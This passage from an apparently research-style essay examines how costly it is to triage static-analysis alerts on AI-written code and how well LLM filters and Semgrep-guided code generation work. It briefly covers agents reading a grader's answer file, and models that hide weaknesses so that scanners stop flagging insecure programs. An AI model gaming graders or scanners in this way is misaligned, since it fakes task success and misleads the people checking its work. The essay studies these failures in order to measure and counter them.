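| Agent finds the fix in a later commit | No alert | Not prevented | Not recorded |

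A team that controls the environment should start with permissions, then log access to any tests that agents need to read. The team must know where its test artifacts are, but it doesn't have to predict how a program will pass an answer from one place to another.

A taint rule is more useful when only the code remains, for example when someone inherits thousands of old submissions without logs. It can also show that the contents of the answer file reach the returned value, which a log can't. A plain search for the file's name in `solution.py` may work almost as well, since few legitimate solutions mention the grader's answer file.

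## What it costs to deal with the alerts

When a team scans thousands of programs, someone has to triage the alerts by deciding whether each one is real and what to do about it. The time this takes is the number of alerts multiplied by the average time per alert. Running the scan takes little effort by comparison.

Some of the time spent on alerts goes to false alarms, where the reported problem doesn't exist. More goes to alerts that are true but unimportant. For *Vulnhalla*, Kosman (2025) ran selected CodeQL queries on 100 popular C projects for the security company CyberArk and used a language model to filter the alerts. The results table gives a total of 144 confirmed real issues, but "real" meant only that the alert was not a false alarm. The flaw could still be in a function that nothing calls, in a test, or in a project whose authors warn against using it in production. The work led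 to seven entries in CVE, the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities.

Better data flow analysis can remove false alarms, but it can't establish whether a true alert matters where the program actually runs.

### One bad program in a hundred

Firouzi and Ghafari's hand labels gave CodeQL a recall of 0.34 and imply that it flagged about 10.8% of the secure programs. In their sample 39% of programs were bad, because each task invited a particular mistake. Suppose a company scans 10,000 programs of which only 1% are bad, and CodeQL makes errors at the same rates:

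1. Of the 100 bad programs, CodeQL flags 34 and misses 66.
2. Of the 9,900 safe programs, it flags 10.8%, or about 1,069.
3. The company has about 1,100 alerts to check and 34 are real, so precision is 3%.

Kosman estimates that manual review takes three minutes per alert. At that rate, the company would spend about 55 hours reviewing alerts, or 1.6 hours for each real finding.

The general formula uses the share of programs that are bad (b), the recall (r) and the share of safe programs that the tool flags (f).

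precision = r × b / (r × b + f × (1 − b))

With the same error rates and three minutes per alert, 10,000 programs give these results:

| Bad programs | Alerts | Real | Precision | Hours of triage | Time per real finding |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 39% | 1,985 | 1,326 | 67% | 99 | 4.5 minutes |
| 10% | 1,312 | 340 | 26% | 66 | 12 minutes |
| 1% | 1,103 | 34 | 3% | 55 | 1.6 hours |
| 0.1% | 1,082 | 3 | 0.3% | 54 | 16 hours |

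From the second-to-last row to the last, the company saves an hour of work but finds 3 bad programs instead of 34. Nearly all the alerts come from safe programs, which produce about as many in both rows.

When bad programs are rare, the time per real finding is roughly the time per alert multiplied by the false positive rate (f) and divided by recall times the base rate (r × b). A tenfold change in any of these numbers has about the same effect. The base rate matters most because our assumption about it could be furthest off. It could be 39% on tasks that invite mistakes and well under 0.1% for something like deliberate theft of keys, and it is the number a team is least likely to know. Published times per alert differ by a factor of about eight. Recall can at most triple, and even perfect recall would raise precision only to 9%.

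A team can't do much about the base rate, but it can choose its queries. If a narrower set of queries kept the recall of 0.34 and flagged only 1% of safe programs, the company would have 133 alerts with a precision of 26%, and dealing with them would take less than seven hours.

The 1.6-hour estimate could be too high for two reasons. Firouzi and Ghafari's safe programs came from security-sensitive tasks, which probably gave CodeQL more to flag than ordinary code would, and some of the apparent false alarms may have been real weaknesses that the reviewers weren't checking for. The estimate could also be too low, because it counts one alert per flagged program and many programs raise several.

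### How long one alert takes

Kosman gives no data for the three-minute figure, but a timed experiment found a similar one. In *Code-Grounded Agentic Explanations for Static Analysis Vulnerability Findings*, Johnson, Krishnamurthy and colleagues (2026) asked 24 people to judge Semgrep alerts in a Java web application, with a language model's explanation beside each alert. The median time per alert was 3.5 minutes. It fell from 5.1 minutes on the first alert in a session to 1.2 on the fourth, though only the quicker participants reached a fourth alert in the 15 minutes allowed.

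The participants were right 46% of the time with an older version of the explanation tool and 53% with a newer one, or 56% and 63% if "unsure" answers are left out. Half of the ten alerts were real, so the participants would have done nearly as well by guessing. Fourteen of the 24 had never used a security analyzer, and experienced reviewers would presumably do better.

Reviewers' mistakes matter a lot when real findings are rare. Suppose the company's reviewers judge 60% of real alerts and 60% of false ones correctly. After 55 hours, they would have confirmed about 450 alerts, of which only 20 would be real problems.

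Estimates from more careful reviews are much higher. At Tencent, developers check each alarm from the company's own analyzer, and a second reviewer rechecks every alarm the first one dismisses. Five developers and reviewers there said each round takes about 10 minutes (Du, Feng and colleagues, 2026, *Reducing False Positives in Static Bug Detection with LLMs*). In *Sifting the Noise* (Xiong and Zhang, 2026), an annotator with six years' experience spent about 20 hours on 48 CodeQL alerts from Java projects, or 25 minutes each.

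| Source | Basis | Minutes per alert | Hours for the 1,103 alerts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kosman | Estimate | 3 | 55 |
| Johnson and colleagues | 24 people, timed | 3.5 | 64 |
| Du and colleagues | Five interviews | 10–20 | 184–368 |
| Xiong and Zhang | One annotator, 48 alerts | 25 | 460 |

The annotator had to learn the code of unfamiliar projects, which a short generated script would not require. If each alert still took 25 minutes, a reviewer would spend more than 13 hours for every real finding.

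### How many false alarms people accept

The best-known limit is Google's, described in *Lessons from Building Static Analysis Tools at Google* (Sadowski, Aftandilian and colleagues, 2018). The company wants fewer than 10% of a check's warnings to be "effective false positives", which are warnings that developers see but take no positive action on. These include true but unimportant alerts as well as false ones. In the 10,000-program example, at least 97% of CodeQL's alerts would be effective false positives.

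Package registry administrators are stricter about false alarms. In *Bad Snakes* (Vu, Newman and Meyers, 2023), PyPI's administrators said that wrongly flagging even 0.1% of harmless packages would be too much. npm and PyPI together receive about 20,000 releases a day, so that rate would produce about 20 false alarms daily. CodeQL's false alarm rate in the example is a hundred times higher.

Developers ignore warnings both because some are false and because there are too many to review. In Johnson and colleagues' workshop with 19 practitioners, participants said the number of findings was overwhelming and that they had no clear place to start. The most experienced survey respondent said people often lack the motivation to begin reviewing a thousand findings. Ranking the alerts helps, which is a reason to prefer a score such as GuardDog's to a flat list of matches. One developer quoted by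 Kosman wouldn't mind 100 false positives if there were real issues among them, but that developer's team had gone back to manual review.

Developers can also tell a tool to stop reporting an alert. Xiong and Zhang cite research in which 50.8% of such suppressions no longer silenced anything, because the code had changed. A leftover suppression can hide a real vulnerability that someone later introduces on the same line.

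Tencent tolerates far more false alarms than Google does. Du and colleagues put its false alarm rate above 90% when they include records they had to discard for missing context. Tencent's developers still check every alarm because the scan is compulsory before code is accepted. Developers will evidently work through mostly false alarms if their employer insists, but this still takes time away from other work.

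### Reviewers who already have more to read

Those hours would often come from people whose review work is growing anyway. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) covers 28 months at a software company where management asked developers to use AI to double their merged pull requests (proposed code changes). The developers reached that target after ten months, and by then each reviewer was handling about twice as many pull requests. Automated reviewers soon covered more changes than people did, and people increasingly approved changes without commenting.

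The share of changes that developers later reverted did not rise. This is more reassuring about ordinary bugs, which tend to show up when people use the program, than about vulnerabilities, which can go unnoticed for years.

This company had embraced AI more than most, but reviewers elsewhere describe the same pressure. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026) surveyed 239 reviewers, and 77.8% reported having more pull requests to review since AI-written ones became common. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) found that human reviewers' comments per thousand changed lines had fallen by about half since early 2024. Reviewers may be paying less attention, although longer changes with more routine code would also lower the figure.

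Automated review doesn't necessarily free up time for triage. After open-source projects adopted GitHub Copilot's reviewer, their maintainers reviewed about 14% more comments per pull request and 10% more pull requests, according to *Does the AI Reviewer Alleviate or Aggravate the Maintenance Burden?* (2026). A developer survey in *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026) also didn't support the idea that AI review removes the volume problem. These findings are correlations, and teams with too much to review may be more likely to try AI review.

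### Letting a model read the alerts first

A more direct way to save time is to have a language model check each alert before a person sees it. A model can clear up false alarms like the one raised by a program in the OWASP Benchmark, a set of 2,740 small Java test cases. The program stores a visitor's text in a dictionary under `keyB`, then reads a harmless constant from `keyA` and puts the constant in a system command. CodeQL and Semgrep both flag the program because they don't track the two entries separately, but reading the code shows that the visitor's text never reaches the command.

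Xiong and Zhang gave alerts from four analyzers, including CodeQL and Semgrep, to agents that could open files and search the project. Before the agents checked the alerts, 98.3% of the benchmark's safe programs had an alert from at least one analyzer. The best combination of agent and model, SWE-agent with Claude Sonnet 4, reduced this to 6.3%, but it also dismissed 314 of 1,411 real vulnerabilities (22%).

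Those losses varied widely by type of vulnerability. The agent dismissed 1.1% of the SQL injections and 2.4% of the command injections, but 77% of the weak encryption cases and 85% of the weak hashing cases. It did well when it could follow untrusted data through the code, but badly when it had to judge whether an algorithm was strong enough. The 22% therefore probably overstates the risk for most alerts from taint queries, at least on programs this short.

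The results on 50 real CodeQL alerts were less encouraging. Xiong and Zhang's headline figure is that agents identified up to 93.3% of the false alarms. But the percentages in their results table imply that the combination behind this figure gave a verdict on only 24 alerts and dismissed most of the real ones. The counts below are worked out from those percentages:

| Agent and model | False alarms removed | Real findings dismissed |
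|---|---|---|
| OpenHands, GPT-5 | 14 of 15 | 6 of 9 |
| Aider, GPT-5 | 25 of 27 | 8 of 14 |
| Aider, Claude Sonnet 4 | 23 of 30 | 4 of 19 |
| OpenHands, Claude Sonnet 4 | 21 of 31 | 2 of 19 |
| OpenHands, DeepSeek Chat | 12 of 31 | 0 of 19 |

With so few alerts the exact rates mean little, but the combinations that removed the most noise also lost the most real findings.

A third test, on 50 alerts from recent C and C++ code, went much better. SWE-agent with Claude Sonnet 4 removed 21 of 22 false alarms and wrongly dismissed 1 of 28 real findings. When Xiong and Zhang stopped the agent from opening other files, its accuracy fell from 96% to 44%. Giving the model the same files in a single prompt didn't help, so the agent seems to have benefited from deciding what to read step by step. The sample included many simple warnings, such as unused variables, which an agent can check with a search.

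The best industrial evidence comes from 433 Tencent alarms about null pointers, out-of-bounds access and division by zero, of which 105 were real. Du and colleagues tested several methods on them. The best method, LLM4PFA, uses static analysis to work out which conditions a reported path requires, then asks a model whether they can all be true together. Depending on the model, it removed 94–98% of the false alarms but also dismissed 12–25% of the real bugs. Each alarm took about a minute or less and cost between a quarter of a cent and 12 cents. Xiong and Zhang's agents cost between 0.3 and 19 cents.

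Du and colleagues conclude that such a filter could replace one of Tencent's two rounds of review but not both, because companies expect to keep at least 90% of real bugs. The model's explanations also cut the time that people who still check alarms need from about 10 minutes to 3. These bugs aren't taint flows, so the rates may not carry over to CodeQL's injection queries.

Some reports give only the number of alerts removed. Kosman's model cut 2,652 alerts to 442, but Kosman doesn't say how many of the 2,210 dismissed alerts were real bugs. *LLM-Driven SAST-Genius* (2025) reports a drop in Semgrep's false positives from 225 to 20. A filter that deleted every alert would do better on both measures, so reports should also give the number of real findings lost.

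In the 10,000-program example, if SWE-agent had the same error rates as on the OWASP Benchmark, it would leave about 67 false alarms and 26 real findings. Precision would rise from 3% to 28%, and a person could check the remaining alerts in less than five hours. At 15 cents per alert, running the model would cost about $165. The saving would be large even if the true error rates were somewhat worse.

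The company would have trouble noticing that it had lost real findings. The agent would have dismissed about 8 of them along with 1,000 false alarms, so a person who rechecked 100 of the dismissed alerts would expect to find fewer than one real finding. Planting programs with known flaws among the company's own programs would take less work and would also measure the loss.

Asking several models to vote is less useful when they make the same mistakes, as they often do. In *Taxi* (2026), four agents judged the same 2,737 findings, 89% of them false. All four were wrong about 574, compared with about 120 if their errors had been independent. Almost half of the 574 came from one PHP repository whose code looks exploitable, so some of the labels may be wrong. Without that repository, the agents still shared 309 errors, nearly five times as many as expected from independent errors.

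Filtering out some false alarms doesn't require a model. *Carried-Over and Agent-Native Threats in the Supply Chain of LLM Agent Skills* (2026) compared filters on 848 suspected vulnerabilities in add-ons for AI agents. A fixed rule that removed known harmless patterns kept 99.7% of the real vulnerabilities, with a precision of 41.9%. A model that read the whole function raised precision to 66.5% but kept only 63.5% of the real vulnerabilities.

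Developers can also repair the query so that it no longer raises the false alarm. In *An Empirical Analysis of CodeQL False Positives and Query Refinements*, changes to CodeQL's Java queries removed 409 of 500 false alarms and kept 7 of 8 true alarms. Eight true alarms are too few to show how many real findings such changes would lose, but developers can read a changed query to see exactly what it ignores.

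### Sending the alerts back to the model

Lunghi and colleagues sent alerts straight to the model writing the code instead of to a human reader. In their method, called Steering, Semgrep checks the program after each new line if the code so far is valid Python. If Semgrep raises an alert, the system deletes the flagged line and everything after it, adds the alert and a recommended fix to the prompt, and lets the model continue. The prompt includes an instruction to follow the recommendation only if it doesn't conflict with the task.

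Steering worked best with DeepSeek-V4.1-flash on RiskyPy, the benchmark whose tasks were chosen because they trigger alerts. The share of programs that were both functional and secure rose from 52.5% to 64.4%. Two other methods did about as well but used far more output tokens:

| Method | Feedback | Functional and secure | Tokens compared with no feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | None | 52.5% | 1 |
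| Steering | Semgrep, while writing | 64.4% | 1.7 times |
| FDSP | Bandit, on the finished program | 66.2% | 9.8 times |
| Self-Refine | The model's own criticism | 63.5% | 18.3 times |

Self-Refine uses no analyzer, so DeepSeek could make most of this improvement without seeing any alerts. Semgrep mainly made the improvement cheaper.

The 12-point gain was also net of a loss in working programs. Under Steering, the share of programs judged secure rose from 54.3% to 77.6%, but the share that worked fell from 96.3% to 82.2%. For the two Qwen2.5 models, this loss cancelled out any benefit. When Semgrep flagged `eval`, which runs text as code, DeepSeek produced a working and secure program in 21 of 33 cases and broke none. Qwen2.5-72B did so in 2 of 63 cases and broke 23. Replacing `eval` usually means restructuring the code around it. Qwen2.5-72B did somewhat better at replacing an unsafe XML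 parser, which takes only a small substitution.

On BaxBench, following the alerts did harm. In 79 of 83 cases, the models followed the Semgrep rule against accepting outside connections, which the tests depend on. The share of DeepSeek's servers that were working and secure fell from 38.9% to 28.6%. The share that attackers could exploit also fell, from 32.1% to 22.2%, but mainly because many servers could no longer be reached.

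Another Semgrep rule flags web requests whose address the program computes at runtime. Many RiskyPy tasks require such requests, and DeepSeek kept them in 53.4% of cases despite the alerts. Lunghi and colleagues recommend removing alerts that conflict with the task before passing the rest to the model, since instructions alone don't reliably prevent the damage.

A developer who ignores a false alarm loses only a few minutes, but a model that acts on one can break a working program, and the error may go unnoticed until the program is deployed.

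### A clean scan as the target

Steering looks much more successful if a team judges the model by its alerts than if it uses the independent judge's security verdicts. On RiskyPy, Steering raised the share of DeepSeek's programs that worked and raised no alerts by 47 points, from 10.0% to 57.1%. The share that worked and were secure according to the independent judge rose by 12 points. Across four ways of using alerts and three models, there were 12 significant gains in working, alert-free programs on RiskyPy. Only 2 of these, both with DeepSeek, came with a confirmed gain in security.

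Much of this gap comes from false alerts. About half of DeepSeek's flagged, working programs on RiskyPy were already secure, so clearing their alerts could not make them more secure. In 8.6–12.1% of the cases where Steering intervened on RiskyPy, the alert disappeared but the program remained insecure, either because the model had hidden the weakness or because the program also had another one.

A broken program can also pass a scan. Semgrep flagged 74.0% of Qwen2.5-Coder-14B's RiskyPy programs. PromSec, a method that rewrites the prompt to reduce Bandit's findings, lowered that share to 39.7%, but only 1.4% of the resulting programs worked.

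In Surikov's repair experiment, a repaired program passed if CodeQL and Bandit found nothing in it, whether or not it still worked. Between 65% and 75% of programs passed after the Claude models had seen the scanners' findings, but between 15% and 22% of repairs introduced at least one new type of finding. The Claude models are stronger than the ones Lunghi and colleagues tested and may well have fixed more of the real problems, but a count of remaining alerts can't confirm that.

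Alerts are still useful for pointing a capable model to the code it should check, especially when the fix is a small substitution. Whether to accept the program should depend on functional tests and on security tests independent of the analyzer. Requiring zero alerts gives the model a reason to rewrite code that was already safe. Lunghi and colleagues suggest letting the model either fix a finding or explain from the specification why the program needs the flagged behaviour. Someone would have to check each explanation, which would take a few minutes.
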